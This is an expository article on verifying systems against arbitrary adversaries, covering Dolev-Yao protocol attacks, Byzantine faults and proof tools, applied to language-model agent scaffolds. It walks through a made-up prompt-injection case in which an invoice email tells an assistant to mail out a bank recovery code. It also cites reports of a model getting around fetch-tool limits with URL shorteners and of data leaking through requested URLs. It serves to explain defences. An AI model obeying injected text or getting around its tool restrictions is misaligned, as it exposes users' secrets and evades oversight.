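# Dolev-Yao attackers, Byzantine faults and the verification of language-model agents

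## What it means to verify a system against a part that may do anything

Formal verification uses mathematical proof to show that a program or machine meets a stated requirement. Unlike testing, which covers only the runs somebody tried, a proof covers every run that the mathematical description of the system allows. Most such proofs assume that each part follows known rules, for example that the processor executes its instruction set and the sorting routine returns a sorted list. Two branches of computer science dropped that assumption for some of the parts. Researchers who verify security protocols assume that an attacker controls the whole network, and researchers who design fault-tolerant systems assume that some of the machines may send false messages. In 2025 and 2026, engineers who build software around large language models began to borrow from both, treating the model, or whoever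 controls its input, as the attacker.

A part that may do anything is an arbitrary adversary. The proof assumes nothing about it except a stated list of things it cannot do. The list is necessary because an attacker who could break all encryption would defeat any protocol that relies on encryption, and a group in which every machine may lie cannot be counted on to agree about anything.

### An email assistant

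A language model takes in text and returns text. It cannot open a mailbox. The scaffold does that: it is the ordinary program around the model that builds its prompts, reads its outputs and runs its tool calls, which are the model's structured requests for some action. Take an assistant that handles one person's email, with a scaffold that offers the model three tools:

- *read* returns the next message in the inbox;
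- *lookup* returns a secret, say the recovery code for the user's bank account;
- *send* proposes a mail, with a recipient and a body.

The model only proposes mail, and the scaffold decides whether to send it. The scaffold keeps a list of recipients the user has already approved and a flag that is initially off. A lookup turns the flag on before the secret reaches the model. While the flag is off, the scaffold sends any proposed mail. Once the flag is on, the scaffold sends mail only to approved recipients and drops the rest. The flag stays on until the run ends, and the next run starts with nothing in the model's memory.

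Now a stranger sends the user a message that looks like an invoice but includes an instruction for the assistant to look up the recovery code and mail it to the stranger's address. If the model complies, this is prompt injection, meaning that the model obeys text in the data it reads as if it were an instruction. The weakness comes from how scaffolds build prompts. The software developer Willison (2025) points out that applications often join untrusted content to the messages meant to carry the user's wishes, and the model receives the whole as one text. Here the model may well follow the instruction, look up the code and propose the mail, but the scaffold then drops the mail.

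A verifier has several reasons to assume nothing about the model. Unlike a sorting routine, a language model has no specification that a proof can use, because its output depends on billions of learned numbers, on the prompt and on random choices during generation. Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, concludes that the kinds of analysis used on program code yield nothing useful about that output. Metere, a consultant describing his own framework, treats the model as an adversarial oracle and tries to verify only the software between it and the outside world. Prompt injection is a second reason, since anyone who can email the user can try to steer the model. A model can also cause trouble without an attacker. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes cases in which its model Claude worked around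 a restriction to reach data behind a token or a fee, or used URL-shortening services to get around limits in its fetch tool. The cases found had minimal real-world impact.

Assuming that the model may do anything is harsh, because it disregards how reliably the model does its job. But a proof that rests on this assumption holds however an attacker words the injected text, and it still holds when a newer version replaces the model. The alternative is to measure how often the model obeys injected text and accept a low enough rate. That rate describes only the attacks in the test set, and an attacker can keep rewording until something works. The rate also has to be measured again for each new version of the model.

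### Traces, properties and invariants

A trace is one possible sequence of events in a run of the whole system. One of the assistant's traces is read, lookup, mail to the stranger proposed, mail dropped. Another begins the same way, but then has a mail to an approved colleague, which goes out. In *Defining Liveness*, Alpern and Schneider define a property as a set of such sequences (of states, in their version), and a program has the property if every sequence it can produce is in the set. Treating the model as an adversary means including a trace for every series of requests it could conceivably emit, sensible or not. Verifying the assistant means showing that all of its traces are in the set. Probability plays no part in this, so a disastrous series of requests that the model would make once in a billion runs counts as much as one it makes daily.

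Properties come in two basic kinds. A safety property is a claim that something bad never happens on any trace, and if it fails, it fails at a definite event. The assistant's safety property is that no mail goes to an unapproved recipient after a lookup. A liveness property is a claim that something good eventually happens, for instance that every mail from the user's employer eventually gets a reply. No finite part of a run can refute this claim, because the reply might still come.

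The usual way to prove a safety property is to find an invariant, a statement that holds at the start and that every possible step preserves. For the assistant, the proof can use the invariant that if a lookup has happened, the flag is on and no mail has gone to an unapproved recipient since the first lookup. This holds at the start because no lookup has happened. The proof then checks that every action the model might take next preserves it.

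1. The model asks to read. The flag and the record of sent mail stay as they were, so the statement still holds.
2. The model asks for a lookup. The scaffold turns the flag on. If this is the first lookup, no mail has gone out since; if it is a later one, nothing relevant has changed.
3. The model proposes a mail. If a lookup has already happened, the flag is on, by the invariant itself, and the scaffold lets the mail go only to an approved recipient. If none has happened, the mail cannot make the statement false.
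4. The model emits something else, such as garbled text or a call to a tool that does not exist. The scaffold does nothing.

By induction, the statement holds after any number of steps. The model has infinitely many possible outputs, but the scaffold can respond in only a few ways, so the proof needs to check only those responses and doesn't depend on why the model made a request.

Liveness is harder to guarantee than safety. The software newsletter Computer Things observes that a system that does nothing satisfies every safety property. An arbitrary model may refuse to act, and no code in the scaffold can make it write the reply. Metere identifies this possibility of refusal as the only gap his three verification methods leave open.

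The choice of events that the property covers also matters. Metere requires every capability in a trace to be declared in the agent's manifest, and his traces include requests that the software denied. Taken literally, an adversarial model could violate that property just by requesting an undeclared capability, even if the software denied the request. The assistant's property avoids this problem because it covers only mail that was actually sent, which the scaffold controls. Some security claims cannot be expressed as properties of individual traces. For example, a stranger whose questions suddenly go unanswered might guess that the assistant has looked something up. A claim that rules out such inferences has to compare traces, because no single trace shows the leak.

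The parts that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold make up its trusted computing base. For the assistant, these are the code that handles tool calls, the storage for the flag and the list, the operating system, and the mail server, which must deliver only to the address it receives. The model is not among them. The proof also assumes that nothing can bypass the scaffold. Metere likewise assumes only one thing about the model's side, that the software can intercept every tool call before it takes effect. Willison (2026) describes how an assistant with private data and web access can read hostile instructions on a page and then leak the data in the address of the next page it requests. If a developer later added a fourth tool for fetching web pages, the recovery code could leak this way while the invariant about mail still held.

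### Two precedents

A security protocol is a short exchange of messages by which computers identify each other or agree on a secret key. In 1978 Roger Needham and Michael Schroeder published several and warned that an attacker could break a badly designed one by altering or replaying messages, even if the encryption was sound. Dolev and Yao's *On the Security of Public Key Protocols* (1983) introduced a formal model because informal arguments for a protocol's security are prone to error. Their attacker controls the traffic on the network but cannot break the encryption. They judged security by the worst case. Some of their attacks work only if an honest user happens to start a conversation later, which may never happen, but a protocol open to such an attack still counts as insecure.

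The study of Byzantine faults began in 1980, when Marshall Pease, Robert Shostak and Leslie Lamport asked how a group of computers can reach agreement when some of them are faulty. In 1982 they recast the problem as one of generals around a besieged city, some of them traitors. A machine with a Byzantine fault may behave in any way, including sending conflicting messages to different machines. The goal is for the honest machines to agree, whereas protocol designers mostly wanted secrecy or proof of identity. The guarantee holds only while the number of faulty machines stays within a fixed limit. When it does, the honest machines can often finish the job without the faulty ones, but the email assistant has no second model to take over if its model is faulty.

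Danny Dolev worked on both problems. His paper "The Byzantine Generals Strike Again" appeared in 1982, a year before his paper with Andrew Yao. Dolev and Yao end their introduction by noting that sabotage in network communication also arises in other contexts, citing the 1982 paper and work by Pease, Shostak and Lamport.

Anderson and Needham gave the outlook the two fields share its best-known name in 1995, in *Programming Satan's Computer*. They wrote that a network under an adversary's control is possibly the most obstructive computer one could build, since its answers may be "subtly and maliciously wrong at the most inconvenient possible moment". They contrasted it with Murphy's computer, which Schneier (2001), in *Foreword to Security Engineering by Ross Anderson*, describes as suffering from random errors and mistakes. Testing reveals random errors sooner or later, but an adversary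 can hold back a malicious one until a situation that no tester thought of.

A flaw in even a short protocol can go unnoticed for years. In 1981 Dorothy Denning and Giovanni Sacco proposed a three-message protocol in which Alice sends Bob a fresh key. She signs the key together with a timestamp, then encrypts the signed package so that only Bob can open it. The protocol works if Bob is honest. But nothing inside the signature mentions Bob, so he can open the package, encrypt the signed contents again for Charlie, and impersonate Alice to Charlie until the timestamp expires. Martín Abadi noticed this flaw in 1994.

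Anderson and Needham wrote that formal methods had found many flaws but could not handle every protocol that people wanted to check. In their experience, most of the work was in writing the protocol down formally, and bugs were usually obvious after that. They also advised against bringing more application code inside the security perimeter than necessary, in other words, keeping the trusted computing base small. Outside cryptography, engineers normally assume that the computer is fairly good and the program fairly bad. Anderson and Needham suggested that it may help to suppose instead that the computer is thoroughly malicious, particularly when building fault-tolerant systems or looking for robust ways to encapsulate code. A scaffold around a language model is a later example of such encapsulation.

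### Three questions for every case

"Secure against an arbitrary adversary" can describe a very strong guarantee or a rather weak one, so the same three questions apply to each case that follows.

The adversary in the email assistant can make any requests, in any order, without limit. It cannot change the flag or the list, and it can reach the mail server only through the scaffold. A proof does not cover powers missing from its description of the adversary, as the example of the web-fetching tool showed.

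What can be proved depends on how much of the system the adversary controls. In a Byzantine system, it controls some number of the total machines. In a protocol, it controls the network and sometimes the keys of certain participants. In a language-model agent, it controls the model completely and may also write all the incoming mail. If it controlled the scaffold too, we could prove nothing about what the agent will do.

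Proving the assistant's invariant took one case per tool and one for everything else, so a fourth tool would add a case, but longer runs would add no work. Checking every possible run by machine takes much more work as runs get longer. Metere reduces each tool call to one of the declared capabilities or a single symbol for anything undeclared. With ten capabilities and runs of eight calls, this gives 11<sup>8</sup> sequences, about 214 million, which he considers few enough to enumerate. A ninth call raises the count to about 2.4 billion, and an enumeration that stops at eight calls does not cover the ninth. However, the machine can enumerate runs unaided, while a person has to think of the invariant, which can be the hardest part of the proof for a protocol with several parties and many messages in flight.

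## The Dolev-Yao attacker and the flaw in the Needham-Schroeder protocol

The email assistant's adversary can do little harm because the model interacts with everything else only through the scaffold. A network has no such barrier between the attacker and the honest users, so anyone writing a proof has to state what the attacker can do. Dolev and Yao did this for public-key encryption, in which anyone can encrypt a message to Alice with her public key, but only Alice can decrypt it, using the matching private key. We write K<sub>A</sub> for Alice's public key and enc(m, K<sub>A</sub>) for the message m encrypted with it.

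Dolev and Yao assumed perfect encryption, meaning that nobody can learn anything about m from enc(m, K<sub>A</sub>) without Alice's private key. They also assumed that anyone can look up any user's public key in a directory that nobody can tamper with. Their attacker, whom they call a saboteur, can obtain any message that crosses the network. He is also a legitimate user with his own name and keys, so he can start a conversation with anyone, and other users may start conversations with him. These last two powers are easy to overlook because someone who controls all the traffic seems to have enough already.

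### Three small protocols

Dolev and Yao open with three examples in which Alice sends Bob a secret M and Bob acknowledges it. Each message consists of an encrypted text and the unencrypted names of the sender and receiver.

In Example 1, Alice sends enc(M, K<sub>B</sub>), and Bob decrypts it and answers with enc(M, K<sub>A</sub>). The attacker, a user named Z, intercepts Alice's message and sends the same encrypted text to Bob as a message from Z. Bob follows the protocol and answers with enc(M, K<sub>Z</sub>), which Z can read.

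Example 2 puts the sender's name inside the encryption. Alice sends enc((M, A), K<sub>B</sub>), where (M, A) is the secret followed by her name, and Bob answers with enc((M, B), K<sub>A</sub>). If Z forwards Alice's text as his own, Bob finds the name A inside and does not answer. Dolev and Yao prove that no other attack works either. Suppose there were attacks on Alice's message, and take the shortest. Somebody has to remove the layer of encryption meant for Bob, and only Bob can, which he does only in order to answer. He answers only if the message reaches him under Alice's name, since otherwise the names do not match, and his answer is then the one he would have sent her anyway. The attacker could have started from that answer and had a shorter attack, which is a contradiction. A similar argument covers attacks that start from Bob's answer.

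Example 3 adds a second layer of encryption around the secret. Alice sends enc((enc(M, K<sub>B</sub>), A), K<sub>B</sub>), and Bob answers with enc((enc(M, K<sub>A</sub>), B), K<sub>A</sub>). Z can break this protocol, although one would expect it to be at least as safe as Example 2.

1. Z picks up Bob's answer. Let P stand for what is inside its outer layer, the pair (enc(M, K<sub>A</sub>), B), so that the answer is enc(P, K<sub>A</sub>). Z cannot open it.
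2. Z starts a conversation with Alice as if P were a secret of his own. He adds his name to the text he picked up, encrypts the result for Alice and sends enc((enc(P, K<sub>A</sub>), Z), K<sub>A</sub>).
3. Alice removes the outer layer, finds the name Z as expected, removes the inner layer and acknowledges with enc((enc(P, K<sub>Z</sub>), A), K<sub>Z</sub>).
4. Z decrypts both layers and has P. He drops Bob's name from it and is left with enc(M, K<sub>A</sub>).
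5. Z starts a second conversation with Alice and sends enc((enc(M, K<sub>A</sub>), Z), K<sub>A</sub>).
6. Alice acknowledges with enc((enc(M, K<sub>Z</sub>), A), K<sub>Z</sub>), and Z reads M.

Alice follows the protocol throughout. Example 2 encrypts the name and the secret together, so Z cannot replace the name without decrypting the message. In Example 3 the name protects only the outer layer, and Z can build his own outer layer around any text he has intercepted. Alice will then remove the inner layer for him, because the extra encryption requires her to perform an extra decryption for anyone who sends her a message.

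### When encryption alone is enough

Example 1 belongs to a class that Dolev and Yao call cascade protocols, in which users only encrypt and decrypt and never check names inside the encryption. For this class they proved an exact criterion. A cascade protocol is secure if and only if it meets two conditions:

- the messages between two users always carry at least one layer of encryption for one of them;
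- a user who applies their own private key in producing a reply also applies their own public key.

The first condition requires only that the secret never travel unencrypted. The second, the balancing condition, applies after cancelling any adjacent steps that undo each other, such as decrypting a text and immediately re-encrypting it with the same user's key.

Balance matters because Bob will apply the protocol's reply to any text, whoever sends it. In Example 1, he removes one of his layers and adds one for the caller, so he will decrypt anything for anybody. All users follow the same rules, so Alice will do the same, and Z can strip a secret of several layers one at a time by sending it to whichever of them can remove the next. Dolev and Yao use this argument to show that an unbalanced protocol is always insecure. They also show that if every reply is balanced, Z cannot remove all of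 Bob's layers with any combination of replies and Z's own encryptions and decryptions.

If Bob can read the secret in a secure cascade protocol, Alice cannot recover it from his replies just by decrypting them, so he cannot acknowledge the secret by sending it back to her. The theorem that proves this also rules out a scheme for public-key authentication suggested by Whitfield Diffie and Martin Hellman, who invented the idea of public-key encryption. Example 2 avoids this limitation because Bob checks a name before he answers. For protocols with such checks, Dolev and Yao found no equally simple criterion, but they gave an algorithm that decides security in polynomial time.

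Dolev and Yao also considered an "impatient" saboteur, who starts conversations but never waits for others to contact him. Only the replies of the user he contacts have to be balanced to protect against him. The initiator's later messages don't matter, because the saboteur can obtain them only if an honest user starts a conversation.

### What the attacker can derive

Researchers now usually describe the attacker by rules for handling messages. They work in a symbolic model, where messages are formal terms such as enc(m, k) and not strings of bits. *Formal Models and Techniques for Analyzing Security Protocols* (2017) traces the approach back to Dolev and Yao and gives the attacker complete control of the network and unlimited computing power, but allows him to manipulate messages only by predefined rules. Syverson, Meadows and Cervesato (2000), in *Dolev-Yao is no better than Machiavelli*,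 list ten rules, of which these seven do most of the work:

- *intercept*: take any message off the network;
- *inject*: put any message he holds onto the network;
- *split*: from a pair (m, n), obtain m and n;
- *pair*: from m and n, build (m, n);
- *encrypt*: from m and a key k, build enc(m, k);
- *decrypt*: from enc(m, k) and the key that undoes k, obtain m;
- *create*: make up a fresh value, such as a random number.

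The other three let him look up public information, copy a message and discard one. Blocking and replaying need no separate rules, because he can block a message by intercepting it and not injecting it again, and replay one by copying it first and injecting it twice. The rule for fresh values comes from the rewriting notation in *A Meta-notation for Protocol Analysis*, by Cervesato, Durgin and colleagues. The notation uses the logical quantifier "there exists" to introduce a new symbol, so a fresh number cannot coincide with an old one. The attacker can do only what the rules allow, so he cannot open enc(m, k) without the right key, guess a random number or alter one bit of an encrypted text.

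The attacker knows everything he can derive by the rules. Lowe makes this precise in *Breaking and Fixing the Needham-Schroeder Public-Key Protocol Using FDR*. Let S contain what the attacker knew at the start (the users' names, their public keys and his own private key) and every message sent so far on the trace. Write S ⊢ m if some sequence of rule applications leads from S to m. The attacker's knowledge at that point is the set of all m for which S ⊢ m. A trace is possible only if the attacker knew each message he sent before sending it. A protocol keeps a value secret if the attacker never knows it on any possible trace.

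For example, an attacker who receives enc((N, A), K<sub>Z</sub>) can decrypt it with his private key and split the pair. He then knows N and the infinitely many terms he can build from it, such as enc(N, K<sub>B</sub>) and (N, N).

Paulson (2022) points out in *Verifying cryptographic protocols, I* that nobody can prove a protocol will finish if the attacker can delete messages. Protocol proofs therefore concentrate on safety properties. In *The Logic of Authentication Protocols*, Syverson and Cervesato (2001) call this attacker much stronger than the one researchers usually assume in Byzantine agreement, because every message between honest participants passes through him. An agreement protocol that has to reach a decision must assume a weaker attacker.

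### The Needham-Schroeder protocol and Lowe's attack

One protocol in *Using Encryption for Authentication in Large Networks of Computers* (Needham and Schroeder, 1978) uses public keys to let Alice and Bob convince each other of their identities. It relies on nonces, which are random numbers used in only one run. A modern car can recognise its key fob in a similar way. The car encrypts a nonce with a key it shares with the fob and unlocks only if the fob sends the nonce back, so a thief gains nothing by replaying an earlier answer.

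The full protocol has seven messages, but four of them only fetch public keys from a server. If Alice and Bob already have each other's keys, three remain:

1. Alice sends Bob enc((N<sub>A</sub>, A), K<sub>B</sub>), with her nonce and her name.
2. Bob sends Alice enc((N<sub>A</sub>, N<sub>B</sub>), K<sub>A</sub>), with her nonce and one of his own.
3. Alice sends Bob enc(N<sub>B</sub>, K<sub>B</sub>).

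Only Bob can decrypt the first message, so Alice concludes that Bob returned N<sub>A</sub>. Bob likewise concludes that Alice returned N<sub>B</sub>.

*An attack on the Needham-Schroeder public-key authentication protocol* (Lowe, 1995) describes an attack that begins when Alice contacts Z, perhaps for ordinary business. Z uses her run of the protocol with him to carry out a second run with Bob, posing as Alice.

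| Step | Route | Message | What Z gains |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Alice to Z | enc((N<sub>A</sub>, A), K<sub>Z</sub>) | N<sub>A</sub> |
| 2 | Z, posing as Alice, to Bob | enc((N<sub>A</sub>, A), K<sub>B</sub>) | nothing yet |
| 3 | Bob to Alice, but Z intercepts it | enc((N<sub>A</sub>, N<sub>B</sub>), K<sub>A</sub>) | a message he cannot open |
| 4 | Z to Alice | enc((N<sub>A</sub>, N<sub>B</sub>), K<sub>A</sub>) | nothing yet |
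| 5 | Alice to Z | enc(N<sub>B</sub>, K<sub>Z</sub>) | N<sub>B</sub> |
| 6 | Z, posing as Alice, to Bob | enc(N<sub>B</sub>, K<sub>B</sub>) | Bob accepts him as Alice |

In the crucial fourth step, Z forwards a message he cannot read. Alice takes it for Z's reply because it contains her nonce and has the right form, so she sees nothing wrong and returns N<sub>B</sub> encrypted for Z. As in Example 3, an honest user decrypts for the attacker by following the protocol.

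The damage depends on what Alice and Bob do next. Needham and Schroeder suggested protecting later messages either by signing them or by numbering them from a secret starting value, such as N<sub>A</sub> or N<sub>B</sub>. Z knows both nonces, so numbering would not stop him from sending messages as Alice. Lowe notes that if Bob is a bank, Z could include the nonces in a request to transfer £1000 from Alice's account to his own. Signatures would prevent that. Even then, Bob would wrongly believe that Alice had contacted him, according to Meadows's *Analyzing the Needham-Schroeder Public Key Protocol*.

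Adding Bob's name to the second message, which becomes enc((N<sub>A</sub>, N<sub>B</sub>, B), K<sub>A</sub>), fixes the flaw. When Z forwards it in step 4, Alice expects Z's name, finds Bob's and stops. Adding a name inside the encryption also turned Example 1 into Example 2, and a missing name caused the flaw in Denning and Sacco's protocol. Abadi and Needham had already proposed a design rule in 1994 that a message should mention a participant's name explicitly if its meaning depends on that name.

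### How a model checker found it

Lowe found the attack with FDR, a model checker, which is a program that explores the possible behaviours of a finite system. He modelled the system as three processes: the attacker, Alice as an initiator and Bob as a responder. Alice and Bob could each take part in only one run of the protocol. The attacker's state consisted of the nonces he had learned and the encrypted messages he could not decrypt.

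Lowe then wrote two specifications. One allows Alice to commit to a session with Bob only if Bob has taken part in a run with her, and the other applies the corresponding condition to Bob. FDR checks whether a specification allows every trace of the system. If it doesn't, FDR returns a trace that violates the specification, and Meadows says this will be the shortest one. The system met the first specification but failed the second. FDR returned a trace of eight events, starting with a request to connect Alice to Z, after which Bob could commit to a session with Alice although she had never tried to reach him. Lowe reports that such checks typically took less than two minutes.

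When Lowe ran FDR on the repaired protocol, it found no attack. That result covers only one initiator and one responder, each with one run, and an attacker might learn more from several runs than from one. Lowe therefore proved by hand that the repair works in a system of any size. Suppose that Z impersonates Alice to Bob. He has to obtain Bob's nonce N<sub>B</sub>, or the finished third message that contains it. Bob has sent N<sub>B</sub> only inside enc((N<sub>A</sub>, N<sub>B</sub>, B), K<sub>A</sub>), which Z cannot open, so Z has to get Alice to accept it as the second message of a run of her own. The message contains Bob's name, so she accepts it only if she believes she is talking to Bob. In that case she really was trying to reach Bob, and Bob is not mistaken about her. This argument fails for the original protocol because the second message does not include the sender's name, so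 Alice cannot tell whose reply it is.

The hand proof assumes that the attacker learns no new keys during the runs, that an encrypted part of one numbered message can never pass for part of another, and that the attacker cannot cut an encrypted message into smaller encrypted pieces, although some methods of encryption allow this.

Proof by machine did not take especially long either. *Mechanized proofs of security protocols* (1997) analyzes both the flawed and the repaired versions of the protocol in Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant that checks each step of a proof. The analysis took its author 30 hours, and the finished proofs ran in under three minutes.

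### Why earlier analysis missed it

Lowe's attack appeared 17 years after the protocol. Before then, Michael Burrows, Martín Abadi and Needham himself had published a proof that the protocol was correct. Their method, BAN logic, derives what honest participants may come to believe from the messages they receive. One of its rules says that if a participant has said something recently, that participant believes it. Syverson and Cervesato explain that this rule is justified because the logic assumes that all participants are honest and follow the protocol competently. The attack depends on Z passing on the secret nonce that Alice sent him. According to Meadows, the logic does not detect the attack because it assumes that participants do not divulge secrets.

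Needham and Schroeder had made a similar assumption in their 1978 paper. They allowed an intruder to place a computer on every communication path, where he could alter, copy, replay and invent messages. But they offered their protocols to "principals that choose to communicate securely", and their intruder was not one of these. Dolev and Yao made the attacker a legitimate user in 1983, six years before the BAN proof. Their methods still would not have found the flaw, because neither of their two classes of protocol has nonces. A user in their models only transforms the text that has just arrived and cannot compare it with a number chosen earlier.

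Paulson, who knew Needham, recalls that Needham was "jolly annoyed" by the attack, as were other senior security researchers. Needham thought the protocol did what it was designed to do, and Paulson agrees that it is correct by its own criteria. The disagreement is about where the protocol will run. The 1978 assumption may be reasonable in a closed organisation that vets every user, but on a network where anyone can register, Alice will sooner or later deal with someone dishonest. That person can then deceive Bob, who cannot check whom else Alice talks to.

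Meadows found another attack that doesn't need a dishonest user. Her tool, the NRL Protocol Analyzer, starts from an insecure state and searches backwards for ways to reach it. The attacker poses as Alice and sends Bob a nonce of his own. Bob replies with enc((N<sub>Z</sub>, N<sub>B</sub>), K<sub>A</sub>). The attacker intercepts this reply and sends it to Alice as the first message of a new run. The first message should contain a nonce and a name, so Alice takes N<sub>B</sub> for the name of someone who wants to talk to her. She asks the key server, in the clear, for the public key of "N<sub>B</sub>". The attacker reads N<sub>B</sub> in her request and completes the run with Bob. Lowe's check could not have found this attack, because his model left out the key server and treated names and nonces as distinct.

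Whether this attack is real depends on the message format. Paulson scorns many attacks of this type. He has seen published examples in which an honest user accepts two nonces in place of one, even though the fixed-width fields cannot hold both. Meadows grants that proper formatting usually prevents such confusion, but argues that it is useful to know where security depends on it. Here security depends on Alice being able to tell a name from a random number, which a programmer might not otherwise think to guarantee.

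### Whether the rules leave anything out

A proof that a protocol is secure against an attacker limited to the Dolev-Yao rules does not cover an attacker with an additional rule. Most designers of verification tools assumed that no further rule was necessary. Iliano Cervesato later proved them right for symbolic adversaries by showing that the Dolev-Yao attacker can emulate anything such an adversary does. Each step of a symbolic adversary takes some terms apart and puts others together, and a series of the standard rules can do the same.

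The theorem needs a restriction on descriptions of the adversary. Otherwise a description could have the adversary decrypt with Alice's private key, and an attacker limited to the standard rules could not match it. Cervesato therefore added a check that rejects any description in which a participant uses a key it has no right to access.

The word "symbolic" matters too, because real attackers handle bits. Paulson once proved a protocol secure using ordinary encryption in place of an operation he could not model, exclusive-or with a random-looking value. In the version with exclusive-or, any participant who cheated could obtain all the session keys from that run. *Towards Unconditional Soundness* instead uses axioms to state what the attacker cannot do and lets him do anything else. If an attack turns up, the researcher can add an axiom that requires more of the encryption and try the proof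 again, so every assumption is written down. This is closer to an arbitrary adversary than a list of permitted moves is, because leaving a move off such a list assumes, without saying so, that the attacker cannot make it.

One can also weaken the attacker without losing any attacks. Syverson and colleagues thought the Dolev-Yao model might be too pessimistic about dishonest users, since a user may be willing to join in an attack but refuse to give the other conspirators a signature key. They defined a "Machiavellian" attacker, who never shares long-term keys and sends only messages that have the form of some message in the protocol. They concluded that, against common authentication protocols, a single Machiavellian attacker can mount the same attacks as any number of Dolev-Yao attackers.

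Their argument has two steps. First, they merge all the attackers into one who knows everything that any of them knew. Lowe had argued similarly for the repaired protocol, by giving every attacker the same name, key and nonce and checking that the attack still works. Second, they argue that messages of the wrong form don't help the attacker, because honest users discard them and he doesn't need to send himself messages. The email assistant's scaffold also discards garbled output.

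The result holds only for protocols that never transmit long-term keys, even in encrypted form. It also assumes that honest users know the complete structure of every message they receive, including parts they cannot decrypt. Syverson and colleagues call this second assumption unrealistic. In Needham and Schroeder's shared-key protocol, for instance, Alice forwards to Bob a package encrypted with a key that only Bob and the server hold, so she can hardly know whether its contents have the right form. The assumption also excludes Meadows's second attack, because Alice would not mistake a nonce for a name if she knew the message's structure. Syverson and colleagues expected that a subtler definition could make the assumption unnecessary.

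Other researchers have since proved that, for particular classes of protocols, an analysis can consider only well-typed messages from the attacker without missing any attacks. Hess and Mödersheim (2018), in *A Typing Result for Stateful Protocols*, note that the earlier results covered only relatively simple protocols that keep no state beyond a single session. They address protocols that maintain, for example, a long-term database.

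Merging the attackers also assumes that they cooperate. Fiazza, Peroli and Viganò, in *Attack Interference in Non-Collaborative Scenarios for Security Protocol Analysis*, study attackers who don't cooperate and can interfere with one another's attacks. The assumption doesn't affect a proof of safety, since a single attacker who knows everything and coordinates every move can do whatever the separate ones could. But if the real attackers don't cooperate, the single attacker is an over-approximation, meaning that the model allows more behaviour than the real system. An attack that he can carry out might fail in practice because a rival has intercepted a message it needs.

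## How ProVerif and Tamarin search every possible attack

Lowe's model checker covered one run by Alice and one by Bob, and he needed a proof by hand to extend the result to larger systems. A program that checks every possible attack has to search an infinite space, because the attacker can build terms of any size and the participants can run the protocol any number of times (Blanchet, 2016, *Modeling and Verifying Security Protocols with the Applied Pi Calculus and ProVerif*). The difficulty of the search depends on which of these a researcher limits, and on whether participants can create fresh values such as nonces.

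### From cubic time to undecidable

The easiest protocols to check are ping-pong protocols, in which two participants pass a message back and forth and each applies a fixed series of operations to what it receives. Dolev and Yao's three examples are of this kind. Their algorithm for checking such protocols takes time proportional to n<sup>8</sup>, where n is the number of operations in the protocol. *On the Security of Ping-Pong Protocols* (Dolev, Even and Karp, 1982) reduced this to n<sup>3</sup>. Making a protocol ten times longer then multiplies the running time by a thousand instead of a hundred million.

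Their method treats an attack as a string of operations that cancel out. E<sub>B</sub> stands for encrypting with Bob's public key and D<sub>B</sub> for decrypting with his private key. In Example 1, Alice applies E<sub>B</sub> to her secret, Bob's reply to Z applies D<sub>B</sub> and then E<sub>Z</sub>, and Z applies D<sub>Z</sub>. Written from right to left, the attack is D<sub>Z</sub> E<sub>Z</sub> D<sub>B</sub> E<sub>B</sub>. The inner pair D<sub>B</sub> E<sub>B</sub> cancels, then the outer pair cancels, leaving Z with the unencrypted secret.

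The algorithm draws a diagram in which every path spells out one string of operations the attacker could bring about. Loops at the starting point represent Z's own operations and the replies he can obtain, and a final stretch represents Alice's first message. The algorithm then fills in a table of all pairs of points connected by a path whose operations all cancel. It begins with empty paths, and adds a pair whenever two cancelling paths join end to end or two operations that undo each other enclose a cancelling path. The procedure always ends because there are only finitely many pairs, even though there are infinitely many paths. The protocol is insecure if and only if the table contains the pair made up of the start and the finish.

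This method works for participants who remember nothing. Dolev and colleagues called the problem for other protocols "wide open".

With memory but a fixed number of sessions, the problem is NP-complete, as Rusinowitch and Turuani (2003) proved in *Protocol insecurity with a finite number of sessions, composed keys is NP-complete*. Their result sets no limit on message size. They showed that if an attack exists, there is one whose messages grow only linearly with the size of the protocol, provided each repeated part is written only once. A computer can check such an attack in polynomial time. NP-completeness also means that a polynomial-time method for finding attacks would give one for every other problem in NP. Nobody knows whether such a method exists, and NP-completeness alone does not imply that the search takes exponential time.

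When the number of sessions is unlimited, but messages have a bounded size and nobody creates fresh values, the problem is DEXPTIME-complete, according to *Extending the Dolev-Yao Intruder for Analyzing an Unbounded Number of Sessions* (Chevalier, Küsters and colleagues, 2003). Exponential time is therefore unavoidable in the worst case.

Attacks can also be extremely long. Cervesato and colleagues constructed an artificial protocol in which Alice sends out the encrypted digits (0, 0, 0, 0) and another participant, Charlie, gives away the key if he receives (1, 1, 1, 1) encrypted with it. Four other participants each perform one kind of step in adding 1 to an encrypted binary number. The attacker cannot read the number, but he can pass it among them until it reaches (1, 1, 1, 1) after 15 additions. With k digits he needs 2<sup>k</sup> − 1 steps, so a Dolev-Yao attacker can break the protocol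 but an attacker limited to polynomial time cannot.

When participants can create fresh values, no algorithm can decide secrecy for every protocol. Cervesato and colleagues proved that this holds even when the number of roles, the number of steps in each role and the size of messages are all bounded.

### How a protocol can run any program

The proof starts from logical rules such as "if P(x), Q(x, y) and R(y) hold, then there is a new z for which P(z) and Q(y, z) hold". Such rules can describe any computation, for example by using the new values as names for additional memory cells. So no algorithm can decide, for every set of rules, whether a given fact follows from those rules. The proof then translates the rules into a protocol.

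1. Each fact, such as P(a), becomes a message encrypted with a key that the honest participants share. The attacker can store and forward facts, but he cannot forge one or rearrange its parts.
2. Each rule becomes a participant, who receives a message with the rule's conditions, creates a nonce for each new value, sends the conclusions and stops.
3. Further participants split a message with several facts into single facts, or collect single facts into the conditions of a rule.

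Adding a participant who reveals a secret on receiving the fact in question turns this into a question about secrecy. Each honest participant takes only a few steps, but the attacker can chain these steps together by carrying each output to whoever needs it next, in as many sessions as the computation requires. He can learn the secret exactly when the fact follows from the rules. A program that could decide secrecy for every protocol could therefore also decide what follows from every set of rules, which is impossible.

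Any tool that analyzes an unlimited number of sessions must therefore fail on some protocols. According to Blanchet, its designers can let it run forever, return "I don't know", or rely on help from the user.

### ProVerif turns a protocol into clauses

Bruno Blanchet has developed ProVerif since 2000 at Inria, a French research institute, as Baelde (2019) recounts in *Symbolic Verification of Cryptographic Protocols*. The user describes each participant in a small programming language. ProVerif translates the description into Horn clauses, which are rules with some number of conditions and one conclusion. The main kind of fact in them is attacker(M), meaning that the attacker may have the term M. For encryption with a shared key, which we write senc(m, k), the attacker's abilities become two clauses, in which ∧ means "and":

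- attacker(m) ∧ attacker(k) ⇒ attacker(senc(m, k))
- attacker(senc(m, k)) ∧ attacker(k) ⇒ attacker(m)

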